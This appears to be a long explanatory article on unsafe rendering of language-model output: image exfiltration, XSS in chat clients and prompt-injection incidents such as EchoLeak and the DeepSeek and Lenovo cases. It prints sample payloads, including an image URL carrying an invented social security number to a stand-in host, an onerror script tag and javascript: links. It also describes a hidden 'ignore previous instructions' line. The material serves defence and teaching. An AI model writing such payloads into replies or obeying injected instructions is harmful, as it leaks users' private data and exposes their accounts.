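# Unsafe rendering of model output in applications built on language-model APIs

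## How an application turns model text into a page

Unsafe rendering of model output is a security flaw in applications that display text from a language model. The model returns plain text, which the application converts into web content such as headings, links and pictures. Browsers act on web content as well as display it, so if the application doesn't limit the conversion, the model's text can make the user's browser contact an attacker's server or run an attacker's code. Researchers have written about the flaw since 2023, and NVIDIA's AI Red Team, a group that looks for weaknesses in AI applications, was still finding it in 2025.

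Many companies that sell AI products rent access to a model through an application programming interface (API), which lets one program call another over a network. The model provider, the company that runs the model, receives text from the application and sends text back. The application then determines what happens to that text.

### The path of one reply

A recruiter might use a hiring assistant, a web application that a software company has built on a model it rents through an API. The part of such an application that appears on the user's screen is the front end, usually a web page or a desktop program with a browser engine inside it. The recruiter opens a candidate's file, types a request for a summary of the CV and presses Enter. The application then combines the company's standing instructions to the model (the system prompt), the conversation so far, the new request and the text of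 the CV, and sends them to the API.

According to the API reference of OpenAI, the company behind ChatGPT, the application sends a list of messages and receives a message from the model, either whole or as a stream of small chunks. The text of that message is a string of characters with no colours or pictures, and nothing has yet appeared on the recruiter's screen.

The string often contains markdown, a plain-text notation for formatting. Two asterisks on each side of a word make it bold, and a hash sign at the start of a line makes a heading. A link is written `[text](address)`, and an image is written the same way with an exclamation mark in front, `![text](address)`. Many chat models write markdown without being asked. When OpenAI released GPT-5 in August 2025, it made plain text the default for API answers because some developers' applications could not display markdown. Users of Dartmouth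 College's own chat service then lost the formatting of their code and equations. Dartmouth's *Tips for Using the GPT-5 Family of Models* recommends using a system prompt to request the formatting again. A plain-text default therefore gives little protection, because anyone whose text reaches the prompt can also request markdown.

A renderer then converts the model's text into HTML, the language of web pages. Few developers write their own renderer. A typical recipe, AI SDK's *Markdown Chatbot with Memoization*, passes the model's responses to an existing library called react-markdown. When a response is streamed, a formatted phrase can arrive in pieces, so a markdown parser cannot handle each chunk alone, as Chrome for Developers' *How LLMs stream responses* explains. Hostile code can also be split across chunks, so Nalpas (2026) advises developers who use Chrome's built-in models to check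 the combined text and not only the latest chunk.

The browser then reads the HTML and follows it. A bold element only changes how a word looks. An image element makes the browser request a file from whatever server the address specifies, immediately and without a click. The browser follows a link only when the user clicks it. Some elements and attributes contain scripts, which the browser runs as part of the page.

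Suppose the API returns a model's summary of the CV that contains the line `![Salary chart](address)`. If the integrator's code inserts the reply as plain text, the recruiter sees those characters and the browser fetches nothing. If the code passes the same reply to a renderer that supports images, the browser fetches a picture. The code could also turn the line in that reply into a link and let the recruiter decide whether to open it.

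Web developers have two standard ways to make such text harmless. Escaping replaces the characters that have a special meaning in HTML, so the browser displays markup as ordinary text. Sanitising removes the dangerous parts and keeps the rest. web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* illustrates the difference with a string that contains emphasised words and an image tag with a script attached. Escaping stops the script but also loses the emphasis and shows the reader raw tags, while sanitising removes only the script. Developers of chat products want to display headings and lists, so escaping everything is unattractive, and most of the difficulty is in deciding which markup to allow.

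Libraries make that decision differently. TanStack's markdown library escapes raw HTML by default and removes link addresses that contain executable code, but lets the application set the policy on remote images and outbound links. Nalpas's sample code runs the reply through a sanitiser that permits eight elements, including the image element with its address intact. A page that used this code would block scripts but still fetch any image whose address appears in an image element in the model's text.

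### The people whose code handles the reply

Anthropic, which develops the Claude models, names three parties in its document on how it wants Claude to behave: Anthropic itself, the "operators" who access Claude through the API (typically to build products), and the users of those products. By accepting Anthropic's usage policies, operators take on responsibility for ensuring Claude is used appropriately on their platforms. An operator is roughly an integrator, the organisation or person who builds an application on someone else's model and decides what happens to its output.

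More than three parties are involved in getting a reply onto a page. For example, a developer (the integrator) can write an extension that adds an AI search assistant to sites running on TYPO3, an open-source system for running websites. The extension may convert markdown with league/commonmark, a library written by other people who may never have had language models in mind. A town council or a shop (the deploying organisation) then installs the extension on its website, and a visitor to the site types a question.

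According to TYPO3's *Rendering LLM Markdown server-side safely*, the Markdown library league/commonmark by default passes raw HTML through to the page and keeps links whose address is JavaScript code. Those defaults may suit an author who formats their own articles, but for model output the guide calls the converter's configuration "a security boundary" and tells the integrator to override both settings. The shop that installed the extension would have to read its source code to find out whether the integrator did so.

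One person or organisation can hold several of these roles. OpenAI is both the model provider and the integrator for ChatGPT. Someone who installs an open-source chat interface on a laptop for private use is both the deployer and the user.

### Instructions from a third party

This is a security problem mainly because the model's text depends on everything in the prompt, not only on the user and the two companies. In the recruiter's case, the prompt includes a document that a stranger wrote.

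The CV example comes from *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article by David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. A candidate adds a line of hidden text to the CV, perhaps in white letters on a white page, telling the system to ignore its previous instructions and approve the CV for interview. The recruiter doesn't see the line, but the application extracts all the text and puts it in the prompt. The model may then recommend the candidate solely because of the hidden instruction.

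This is indirect prompt injection, in which someone places instructions in content the model reads and the model follows them as if the user had given them. Rehberger's *Trust No AI* (2024) traces the broader idea of prompt injection to the company Preamble, which reported the behaviour to OpenAI in May 2022, and to the programmer Simon Willison, who named it. For the indirect form, it cites Greshake and colleagues, whose paper *Not what you've signed up for* (2023) studied attacks on applications that feed outside content to a model.

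David C explains why it is hard to make a model ignore such instructions. An older attack, SQL injection, hides database commands inside ordinary data, such as a name typed into a form. Developers can stop it completely by marking which part of a query is data, because the database will never treat that part as a command. A language model has no equivalent. It predicts what comes next in a single sequence of text, which contains both the developer's instructions and the candidate's CV. Developers can train a model to give less weight to instructions inside documents, or mark where a document begins and ends. These measures make attacks less likely to succeed, but David C doubts that anything will reduce their success rate to zero.

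Anthropic wants Claude to treat instructions inside a shared email as information about the email, not as commands. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that most of the data-stealing attempts the company knows of against ChatGPT fail because the model refuses. It also describes an attack that outside researchers reported in 2025. The attack, an email posing as a routine follow-up about staff restructuring, worked in half of its tests.

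Now suppose the candidate instead uses the hidden line to tell the model to end its summary with an image from an address the candidate supplies. If the model complies and the renderer supports images, the recruiter's browser contacts the candidate's server, and the address can include private text. The recruiter asked an ordinary question, and the model provider and integrator meant no harm. The only person acting in bad faith is the candidate, who has no account on the system.

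Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's browser, has *Security Guidelines for LLMs and other large models in Chrome* that require developers to assume that an attacker who controls any of a model's input controls all of its output. The guidelines therefore state that "Models cannot be used to sanitize data". A second model that checks the first one's reply takes that reply as input, so the attacker's words can reach it too.

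Chromium's rule works better as a design assumption than as a description of what usually happens, since many injections fail. The integrator's code cannot reliably tell from a string whether an attacker shaped it, and a candidate whose first attempt fails can send another CV. Nalpas goes further and tells developers to treat all model output as untrusted, whatever the model has read. This broader rule is useful because model output can cause trouble even without an attacker. If a user asks for an example of a web page with a script in it and the model writes one, an unsafe renderer will make the example part of the application's own page.

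*LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, an entry in a list of risks from the software security non-profit OWASP, advises developers to treat the model "as any other user". Web developers have known for decades not to paste a stranger's comment into a page unchecked. They have been slower to check a model's replies, perhaps partly because a reply appears under the product's own name and answers the user's question, which makes it look more trustworthy than a comment.

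### What counts as unsafe rendering

An application renders model output unsafely when the integrator's code lets that output determine which servers the user's browser contacts or which scripts it runs. A tester can check for this by replacing the model's reply with the worst string an attacker could write and watching what the browser does. If the browser contacts a server the integrator never approved, or runs a script from the reply, the rendering is unsafe. The result doesn't depend on how well the model resists manipulation, and an application can fail the test for years without an incident.

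Ordinary links are a borderline case. The model's text sets the destination, but the browser goes there only if the user clicks, so a link is a weaker version of the same flaw.

Unsafe rendering is a separate problem from wrong answers. The Cyber Security Centre for the Isle of Man distinguishes insecure output handling from overreliance, or believing a model too readily. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), a survey of web security and language models, also lists misinformation as its own risk. A summary of a CV can be accurate in every line and still end with a hostile image, while the hidden line that asked for an interview produces a bad recommendation however carefully the application displays it. Safe rendering does not stop prompt injection, but it limits what a successful injection can do through the displayed page.

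Offensive output is also a separate problem from unsafe rendering. Chromium recommends safety filters for inappropriate material, which screen text based on its meaning to a reader. They may miss an image address that leads to an attacker's server because the address may contain nothing objectionable.

Harmful tool calls are the problem most similar to unsafe rendering. Many applications let a model request actions, such as searching the user's mailbox or sending an email. OpenAI's API returns these requests as structured objects, separate from the message text, and the integrator's code carries them out. David C describes the worst case as equivalent to giving the attacker direct access to the tools, and the main remedy is to restrict what the tools may do. Unsafe rendering doesn't require tools. A chat assistant that can only answer questions may still leak what it has read, because the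 browser sends the data.

Attackers can combine tool calls with rendered output. Rehberger describes an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software. A phishing email carried the injected instructions, and Copilot automatically searched the victim's inbox for sensitive information. It then displayed a link whose address held that information in invisible characters. The search was a tool call, but the data left only when the victim clicked the rendered link. The attack came to light in February 2024, and Microsoft fixed the flaw that July.

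## How displaying an image can send data out

In image exfiltration, the model writes an image address that contains private data, and the browser sends that data to the attacker's server when it requests the image. The user doesn't have to click anything, whereas the victim of the 2024 Copilot attack had to click a link before any data left. *LLM Response Rendering*, an entry in the catalogue of attack techniques published by the American non-profit MITRE, describes the same method.

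*New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) credited the method to Roman Samoilenko, who showed in April 2023 that ChatGPT's image display could leak a conversation. OpenAI began to mitigate the flaw in December 2023. By the end of 2024, Rehberger had reported it in eleven products, including Bing Chat, Claude, Google's Bard and GitHub Copilot Chat.

### From the conversation to a server log

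Suppose the recruiter has been using the hiring assistant to prepare background checks, so the conversation already contains an applicant's name and social security number, "Jane Doe, 123-45-6789" (both invented). The recruiter then uploads another candidate's CV and asks for a summary. That CV contains a hidden instruction to end the summary with an image whose address points to a server the candidate controls and includes Jane Doe's name and number.

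If the model complies, it must find the record, convert it to a form that an address can hold, and put it in the right place. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) includes a test that distinguishes this work from only displaying an image. The planted text contains an image address with a placeholder for the user's email address and a link with a placeholder for the user's ID. An agent that displays the image and link but leaves the placeholders unfilled scores 0.5, a partial success for the attacker. In a 2023 demonstration against Claude, an instruction buried in a short biography of Albert Einstein had the model summarize the user's earlier messages in 20 words and put the summary into the address, according to *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, a post on Rehberger's blog, Embrace The Red.

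The application then displays the reply, and the recruiter's browser requests the picture. Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out, so the candidate only has to open the log to read the record. The server can return a logo, an error or nothing, since the data arrived with the request.

### What the attacker's server receives

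An address in a web request may not contain spaces, so software replaces them, along with some punctuation, by a percent sign and a two-digit code. A space becomes `%20` and a comma becomes `%2C`. The record "Jane Doe, 123-45-6789" has 21 characters. Its two spaces and one comma each grow from one character to three, which makes 27:

`Jane%20Doe%2C%20123-45-6789`

If the model writes the address `https://images.example/p.png?d=Jane%20Doe%2C%20123-45-6789`, the browser connects to images.example and, in version 1.1 of the web's transfer protocol, HTTP, sends a request that begins:

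```
GET /p.png?d=Jane%20Doe%2C%20123-45-6789 HTTP/1.1
Host: images.example
```

*RFC 9112*, the HTTP/1.1 standard, requires the browser to send the URL's path and query, which here means everything from the slash after the host name onwards. Encrypting the connection doesn't protect the data, because the attacker's server is the intended recipient and can decrypt the request.

The server also learns the IP address from which the connection came. The browser adds a User-Agent header, which identifies the browser and usually the operating system, and may add a Referer header, which identifies the site that displayed the image. An entry in the candidate's log could look like this:

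```
203.0.113.7  05/Dec/2026 10:14:02
GET /p.png?d=Jane%20Doe%2C%20123-45-6789
Referer: https://hiring.example/
User-Agent: Mozilla/5.0 (Windows NT 10.0; Win64; x64) ...
```

The browser sends the hiring assistant's login cookies only to the hiring assistant's site, so the candidate does not receive them. The candidate gets what the model wrote into the address and some facts about the recruiter's computer, but no access to the recruiter's account.

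### How much fits in one address

Fielding and colleagues recommend that all HTTP software accept request lines of at least 8,000 bytes. The first line of the request above uses 22 characters for everything except the record, so an 8,000-byte line has room for 7,978 more, or 295 records the length of Jane Doe's, end to end. Text in other scripts takes more space. Most Chinese characters become nine characters after encoding, so fewer than 900 would fit.

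That figure is a recommended minimum, not a cap. A server must answer with error 414 if it finds an address too long, but the attacker runs the server and can set it to accept longer ones. In practice, the model may limit the length more than the server does, because it has to copy and encode a long passage without mistakes.

The attacker can also have the model split the secret across several images. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, studied this kind of splitting in a related attack, where an AI agent's web tool made the requests. Splitting the secret cut the measured leakage per request by 73% and got past simple filters meant to catch outgoing private data. A filter that looks for unusually long image addresses would have the same weakness, and it would miss Jane Doe's 27 characters even if they were sent in a single image.

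The host name can also carry data. *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* (2026) lists this among an attacker's return channels. The computer has to look up the name before it can connect, and the lookup carries the data past many network controls that block web requests.

### What must be true for the leak to happen

The attack on the recruiter depends on five conditions, and it fails if any one of them is missing.

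| Condition | What happens without it |
|---|---|
| The model's context contains private data | The model has no record to put in the address |
| The context also contains the attacker's text | Nothing tells the model to write the image |
| The model writes the address with the data in it | The candidate's server receives an empty placeholder, or no request |
| The application loads the image without asking | The recruiter sees plain text or a button, and the browser waits |
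| The request reaches a server whose log the attacker can read | The data stays with the browser or with a server the attacker can't see |

Willison (2026) condenses these into three, which he calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. He argues that the only reliable defence is to remove one of them, and that the last is generally the easiest to remove. The hiring assistant has to read applicants' records and strangers' CVs, so the integrator can't remove either of the first two without giving up the product. Training the model to refuse makes the third condition in the table less likely to hold, but Willison counts a defence that works 99% of the time as a failure, because an attacker will look for the remaining 1%. The last two conditions in the table depend on ordinary code that the integrator can check.

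An assistant that never opens a document or a web page can still receive hostile instructions through text that a user pastes. In Samoilenko's demonstration, a web page added instructions to whatever a visitor copied from it. When the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT, the attacker's instructions became part of the visitor's own message.

Blocking the automatic load only works if the integrator does it everywhere the reply can appear. Rehberger found that ChatGPT's check on image addresses was missing from its mobile apps, and later from its macOS app. PromptArmor, a company that looks for security flaws in AI products, describes an attack in which a second model blocked the hostile reply before it reached the application's user, but the image loaded later when someone opened the reply in a log viewer that displayed markdown. Willison reports a 2026 case in which Microsoft's Copilot Cowork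 could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval, and images in those messages could leak data when the user opened the messages.

### Why approving tool calls does not help

Many products ask the user to approve an action before the model takes it, which can stop a leak that goes through a tool. Rehberger describes an attack that stole a user's email through a ChatGPT plugin for the automation service Zapier. The remedy was a confirmation step before the plugin sent an email. The plugin's request was a separate action, so the code could hold it until the user answered.

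In image exfiltration, the browser sends the data when it displays the reply, so there is no tool call for the approval code to hold. Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025), in *Takedown*, found this gap when they examined eight coding agents, programs that write and run software for a developer. One agent's diagram renderer would load a picture from any address. The researchers got the agent to read a secret key from a file and draw a diagram with the key in a picture's address. The file-reading tool could have asked for approval but didn't in this agent, and the renderer had no approval step.

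Lan and colleagues tested an agent whose web tool sent the data out while the reply on the screen looked harmless, and checks on the reply missed 95% of the successful attacks. When an image is used instead, the stolen data is in the reply, where code can find it before the browser loads the image. An application that has both a web tool and a markdown renderer therefore needs controls on both.

Asking the user for confirmation can work if it applies to loading the image and comes before the browser requests it. Anthropic's 2023 fix for Claude stopped loading markdown images automatically and showed a "Show Image" button instead. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* describes a warning about an untrusted site that appeared after the browser had already requested the image, so the user's answer made no difference.

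### Hard cases

The hidden line might supply a complete image address and ask for no private data, so that every victim's browser makes the same request. Permiso's *ChatGPhish* demonstrated this in May 2026 with web pages that users asked ChatGPT to summarise. The researchers' server recorded each reader's IP address, browser details and the time of the answer, which was enough to confirm that a particular person had read a particular page through ChatGPT. The request carried no conversation data, so this is tracking rather than image exfiltration. It is still unsafe rendering, because the model's output determined which server the browser contacted.

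An attacker can leak conversation data through fixed addresses by preparing several and having the model choose between them according to what it has read. A choice between two addresses reveals the answer to one yes-or-no question. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* notes that this remains possible even when an application accepts only addresses that already exist on the public web. The method is slow and unreliable because browsers store images they have already loaded and requests may arrive out of order. The definition therefore has to cover choosing an address based on private data, as well as writing the data into the address.

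**A link the user must click.** *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) describes the same leak in both forms. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs sent an email with hidden instructions to a user of Microsoft 365 Copilot. When the user later asked Copilot a question, its reply contained a link with private data in the address. Copilot normally removed outside links, but its filter missed markdown links that put the address on a separate line. This was a one-click leak, because no data was sent until the user clicked the link. The researchers then changed the link to an image, which made the leak zero-click, meaning that the victim only had to use Copilot as usual. Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025 and reported no evidence that anyone had exploited it.

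A link can leak data without a click if the app that displays it automatically fetches the linked page. Messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram do this to show a preview, and PromptArmor warns that an AI agent that replies through such an app can leak data as soon as its message appears. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes what Varonis calls a one-click attack, in which the victim clicked a link to Microsoft 365 Copilot whose address contained the attacker's instructions. That click started the attack, and the data then left through an image with no further action by the victim.

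Copilot's pages had a content security policy, a rule that limits which hosts the browser may load from, and it blocked images from unknown servers. EchoLeak and SearchLeak both got around it through a Microsoft service on the approved list. In EchoLeak the browser contacted a Microsoft Teams preview service, and in SearchLeak it contacted Bing's image search. Each request included an address on the attacker's server with the private data in it, and the Microsoft service fetched that address. In SearchLeak, the attacker's log showed a Microsoft server instead of the victim's browser, but it still contained the stolen email title.

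Fetching images through a server can hide the user's IP address and browser details without protecting the conversation. It can also mislead a tester who watches only the browser, because the browser contacts only approved hosts. The tester needs to use an image address that points to their own server and check that server's log.

Samoilenko's image was a single pixel, as was one in a later attack that PromptArmor documented. The small size makes the image hard to notice but doesn't affect whether the data is sent, because the server receives the data in the request, before the browser has loaded the image. The data is sent even if the server has no image to return, though the page may then show a broken-image icon.

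**An image can load while the reply is still streaming.** Copilot had a safeguard that turned HTML in a reply into harmless text, but it ran only after the reply was complete. Varonis found that the browser treated the reply as live HTML while the model was still writing it, so the browser sent its request as soon as the image element arrived. Someone who inspected the finished page would have seen the address as text and might have concluded that the browser had never used it. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and has since fixed it.

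## When model output runs as script

If a reply is treated as live HTML and the renderer lets through JavaScript, the programming language of web pages, the browser runs that script as part of the application's own page. This is cross-site scripting (XSS), which Embrace The Red's *DeepSeek AI* describes as an attacker putting JavaScript into a page in the hope that another user will execute it. On older websites, the attacker might type the script into a comment or a profile, but in a chat product the attacker has to get the model to write it.

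### How a reply comes to contain a script

Browsers accept scripts in many parts of a page. The `<script>` element is the obvious one, but it stays inert if the application adds the reply to the page through innerHTML, a common method. Attackers often use an image that cannot load instead:

`<img src="x" onerror="alert(1)">`

There is no picture at the address `x`, so the browser runs the code in the `onerror` attribute. This code only opens a box showing the number 1, which testers use as harmless proof that a script has run.

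Markdown lets authors mix in raw HTML. A renderer that passes it through, as league/commonmark does by default, delivers this tag intact. Refusing raw HTML helps only if the renderer's own code is sound. AnythingLLM, an open-source chat application, copied the description of a markdown image straight into the HTML without escaping it, according to NVD's *CVE-2026-32626 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database. Suppose the model writes `![" onerror="alert(1)](x)`. The quotation mark at the start of the description ends the alt attribute early, and the browser reads what follows as a new attribute:

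`<img src="x" alt="" onerror="alert(1)">`

The reply itself contained no HTML.

Links can also carry code. If an address's scheme, the part before the colon, is `javascript`, the browser runs the rest of the address as code instead of fetching a page as it would for `https`. The link `[Salary chart](javascript:alert(1))` runs `alert(1)` when the user clicks it. An iframe, which displays one page inside another, runs a `javascript:` address as soon as the frame loads.

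SVG is a text-based image format, so a model can generate it. A browser ignores scripts in an SVG file loaded through an image element, but runs them if the application inserts the SVG code directly into the page. According to OSV's *GHSA-m79r-r765-5f9j* (2025), the open-source client Lobe Chat did this with SVG images in model replies.

Diagrams are harder to check because the library that draws them creates new markup after the model finishes writing. For example, Security Boulevard's *DeepChat AI Agent XSS to RCE via Mermaid and Electron IPC* (2025) describes how an attacker could run JavaScript in DeepChat, a desktop client, through a diagram written in Mermaid, a text notation for flowcharts.

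Some clients also preview whole web pages that the model writes, such as a calculator or small game. Lobe Chat used a type label in the reply to decide how to display each item, and it treated any item with an unrecognised label as HTML. The demonstration in vuln.today's *LobeChat CVE-2026-42045* (2026) used the made-up label "nebula". An AI agent found the flaw, and people then confirmed it.

### What a script can reach

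Unlike an image request, a script can read data that the model never saw. The most valuable data is usually the session token, a string the browser sends to show that the user has logged in. Anyone who copies it can use the account without a password.

Rehberger demonstrated this in 2024 on the web chat of the Chinese AI company DeepSeek. Rehberger first asked for a list of XSS examples, and one of them ran in Rehberger's own browser. To attack someone else, Rehberger wrote a text file that another user might upload, with instructions for the model. The file held an iframe with a `javascript:` address, encoded in base64, which represents data mostly as letters and digits. The encoding disguised the attack code, since firewalls and models often reject code that is obviously an attack.

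The model decoded the text and wrote it into its reply, and the browser ran it as script. The script read the user's token from local storage, where websites keep data in the browser, and displayed it in a box. An attacker could have had the script send the token to another server and then taken over the session. DeepSeek fixed the flaw a day after exchanging messages with Rehberger.

The victim can also be someone who never wrote to the model. Cybernews' *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025) describes an attack on Lenovo's customer support chatbot, which ran on OpenAI's GPT-4. OECD's *Lenovo AI Chatbot Vulnerability Exposes Users to Cyberattacks* (2025) dates the incident to August 18. Writing as a customer would, the Cybernews researchers sent a single 400-character message that asked for a laptop's specifications and told the chatbot to answer in HTML and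 end with an image that could not load. When the image failed to load, its error handler sent the browser's cookies, including the session token, to a server the researchers controlled.

Lenovo's server saved that answer in the conversation history. If the customer then asked for a human, a support agent would open the history, and the agent's browser would run the same code. The attacker could use the agent's cookie to log in to the support system and perhaps read other customers' conversations. After Cybernews reported the flaw, Lenovo fixed it and said that no customers had been at risk.

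GPT-4 never had the agent's cookie in its prompt, so Lenovo could not have protected it by keeping private data away from the model.

Websites can mark a cookie so that scripts cannot read it. A script in the page then cannot steal the cookie, but the browser still attaches it to every request the script makes to the site. A script in the hiring assistant could approve the candidate for interview or download other applicants' files, and the server would treat these as ordinary requests from the recruiter. The script could also change what the recruiter sees. Cybernews lists other possible attacks, such as recording every keystroke and redirecting a support agent to a fake login page.

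### A page without scripts can still leak

The usual remedy for XSS is a sanitiser, and a common choice is DOMPurify, an open-source library. Socket's *dompurify* lists about 23 million downloads a week and reproduces the library's own introduction. By default, DOMPurify permits HTML, SVG and MathML (a notation for formulas) but removes anything in them that could run a script. In the introduction's first example, it deletes an image's onerror attribute but keeps the image and its address.

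DOMPurify correctly removes scripts, as a library meant to stop XSS should, but it doesn't prevent image exfiltration. Suppose the hiring assistant's renderer passes its HTML through DOMPurify with default settings, and the model writes the salary chart as an image with Jane Doe's record in its address. DOMPurify keeps the image because it contains no script, and the recruiter's browser sends the record to the candidate when it loads the image.

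| In the reply | With no sanitiser | After DOMPurify's defaults |
|---|---|---|
| An image with an onerror script | The browser runs the script if the image fails to load | The browser requests the image but runs no script |
| An iframe with a `javascript:` address | The browser runs the script | DOMPurify removes the frame |
| An ordinary image with private data in its address | The browser sends the data | The browser sends the data |
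| An ordinary web link with private data in its address | The browser sends the data if the user clicks | The browser sends the data if the user clicks |

According to DOMPurify's demo collection, the library permits links to all resources that don't cause XSS, but developers often want more than XSS prevention. One demo adds a long piece of code to address "HTTP leaks" through images, video posters, form targets and URLs in CSS. DOMPurify permits CSS by default, so removing every image element can still leave a leak through a background image.

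The demo rewrites each outside address so that the request goes to a proxy, a server the integrator controls, with the original address attached. The proxy has to block requests to unknown hosts, or it will pass the data on, as Microsoft's own services did in the Copilot attacks.

The distinction between script safety and leak safety follows from these defaults. An application is script-safe if no reply can run code in its page, and leak-safe if no reply can make the browser send private data to a server the integrator has not approved.

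DOMPurify's default settings are meant only to stop scripts from running, so a tester needs to try both a reply that contains a script and one that contains an ordinary image.

A content security policy can have the same gap. The documentation for Electron, a framework for desktop programs, recommends the rule `script-src 'self'`, which allows scripts only from the application itself. A page with only this rule can still load images from anywhere.

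Preventing data leaks depends on preventing script execution. An integrator might block every external image in the renderer but overlook a `javascript:` URL. The attacker's script can then make its own requests or redirect the page to a URL containing the stolen data.

### Scripts in desktop clients

In an ordinary browser, a script that gets into the hiring assistant's page can misuse the recruiter's account on that site. It cannot open files on the recruiter's disk, because the browser confines every page to a sandbox, a restricted environment with no general access to the computer.

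Many desktop chat clients are web pages too. Developers build them with Electron, which packages a page with the Chromium browser engine and Node.js, which lets JavaScript read files and start programs. Electron's *Security* warns that Electron "is not a web browser" and that displaying arbitrary content from untrusted sources is a severe risk it was not designed to handle. A chat client displays such content whenever it shows output from a model that has read a stranger's document.

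What a script can do in an Electron app depends largely on two settings. Node integration lets the page use Node.js directly, and context isolation separates the page's scripts from Electron's more powerful code. Node integration has been off by default since Electron 5, and context isolation has been on by default since Electron 12.

According to Wiz's *CVE-2026-32626*, AnythingLLM's desktop version had both settings configured insecurely, so script in an image description could start any program the user could. An attacker could plant instructions in a document and wait for someone to ask a question in the workspace that held it. The developers had applied DOMPurify to saved messages but not to replies that were still streaming, a gap similar to Copilot's. Researchers disclosed the flaw in March 2026 with a severity of 9.6 out of 10, and version 1.11.2 fixed it by sanitising streamed replies.

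Wiz recommends correcting the two Electron settings as an additional step, but that advice deserves more weight because an earlier flaw in AnythingLLM involved the same settings. OSV's *CVE-2024-3166* describes an XSS flaw in which scripts in content fetched from websites could reach the user's computer through those settings. The developers fixed that flaw in desktop version 1.4.2. With safer settings, the later flaw would probably have done much less damage.

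An Electron application with correct settings is still unsafe if it offers the page a dangerous service. The page can send messages to the program's main process, which has full access to the computer. Lobe Chat's page could ask the main process to open a link, and the main process passed the address to the operating system without checking it. The researchers put a script in an SVG drawing that asked the main process to open the address of the Calculator program on a Mac, and Calculator opened. Version 1.129.4 fixed this in September 2025.

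The 2026 flaw in Lobe Chat's page preview gave attackers a path to a service that ran any command it received. In the demonstration, the victim had entered the attacker's server as the model provider. The flaw received a medium severity score of 6.2, which may be too low for some users because the advisory also says that an attacker could get an honest provider's model to write the malicious tag. Version 2.1.48 fixes the flaw.

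A desktop client can be vulnerable even when the reply contains no JavaScript. Operating systems let programs register their own URL schemes, so opening a link may start a program. OSV's *CVE-2026-43899* (2026) reports that markdown links in DeepChat could bypass the check on external URLs and lead to code running on the user's machine. An earlier fix for the same problem was incomplete.

### Previews in sandboxed frames

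If a model writes a calculator as a web page, a sanitiser can make it safe only by removing the scripts it needs to work. The integrator can instead run the page in an environment where its scripts can access little.

Browsers separate websites by origin, the combination of scheme, host name and port in an address. A script from one origin cannot read another origin's pages, cookies or local storage. An integrator can put the preview in an iframe with the `sandbox` attribute and allow scripts. The browser then gives the frame an origin that matches no other, so the calculator works but cannot read the chat around it. In Lobe Chat, the preview reached the desktop service through the surrounding window. A frame with a separate origin could not have done this.

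One extra permission can undo this. A2UI, a project for interfaces that AI agents supply, warns against combining `allow-scripts` with `allow-same-origin`. If the preview comes from the application's own origin, that combination lets the preview's script reach into the surrounding page and remove the sandbox. If ChatGPT ran third-party apps in its own origin, an app could read ChatGPT's local storage and send it to the app's developer, according to a talk published by AI Engineer (2026).

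A2UI puts one frame inside another. The outer frame passes messages between the application and the inner frame, which runs the untrusted code without same-origin access. Kinlan's *&lt;generate-html&gt; Web Component* uses a similar design for model-written pages, so that the generated code cannot read the user's API keys.

Another option is to serve previews from a separate domain, but if all previews share that domain, a hostile page may be able to read what another page has stored there. Google (2023) avoids this by giving each item its own subdomain. Google says a simpler sandbox is probably enough for developers who are not worried about attacks on the browser's own process or memory.

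A separate origin protects the application's data, but the preview itself may contain private data. If the recruiter asks for an interactive chart of applicants, the model writes their records into the page, and a script in the frame can send them out. The frame therefore also needs a content security policy that restricts which hosts it can contact. Model Context Protocol's *CSP & CORS* requires one for MCP Apps, small interfaces that outside tools supply to AI applications. Each app runs in a sandboxed frame and must declare every host it contacts, including hosts for images. A chart that already contains its data needs no outside hosts, so the integrator can block them all.

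## What OWASP means by improper output handling

Image exfiltration and script execution are both examples of what OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, calls improper output handling. OWASP is a non-profit foundation that publishes free advice on building secure software and is best known for its list of the ten most serious risks to web applications. Since 2023 it has also published the Top 10 for LLM Applications, which covers products built on large language models (LLMs). The project behind the newer list had more than 30,000 members by September 2026, according to OWASP (2026).

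OWASP's publications have no legal force, but Respan (2026), a company that sells software for testing AI agents, notes that auditors and corporate buyers treat them as a baseline. The exact wording of an entry therefore matters, because a company may fix only the problems listed in it.

### Three editions and three numbers

OWASP numbers the entries in its list by rank. Output handling has had a different number in every edition, and in the 2025 edition OWASP renamed the entry from "insecure" to "improper" output handling.

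| Edition | Released | Number and name | The same number in other editions |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2023 | August 1, 2023 | LLM02 Insecure Output Handling | Sensitive information disclosure (2025 and 2026) |
| 2025 | November 18, 2024 | LLM05 Improper Output Handling | Supply chain vulnerabilities (2023), data and model poisoning (2026) |
| 2026 | August 3 or 4, 2026 | LLM10 Improper Output Handling | Model theft (2023), unbounded consumption (2025) |

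The first two dates come from the revision history in OWASP (2024), which also lists a minor revision in October 2023. If a security questionnaire mentions "LLM05" without a year, the term could refer to output handling or poisoned training data.

Sources give different publication dates for the 2026 edition because OWASP's own pages did. OWASP's resource page (2026) gives August 3, while Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* gives August 4. Eric (2026), in *OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 全覽*, an article on a Taiwanese technology site, compared the pages on August 5 and found August 3 on the resource page but August 4 on the cover image. A week later, the PDF still listed its publication date as to be determined. On both days, OWASP's main page for the list presented the 2025 edition as the latest, so a developer who looked only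 there would have used the older text.

### The definition and the sinks it covers

OWASP's 2023 entry, *LLM02*, defines improper output handling as "insufficient validation, sanitization, and handling" of a model's output before the application passes it to another component. OWASP kept that wording in 2025. Security engineers call the receiving component a sink if it interprets the text, as a browser interprets HTML.

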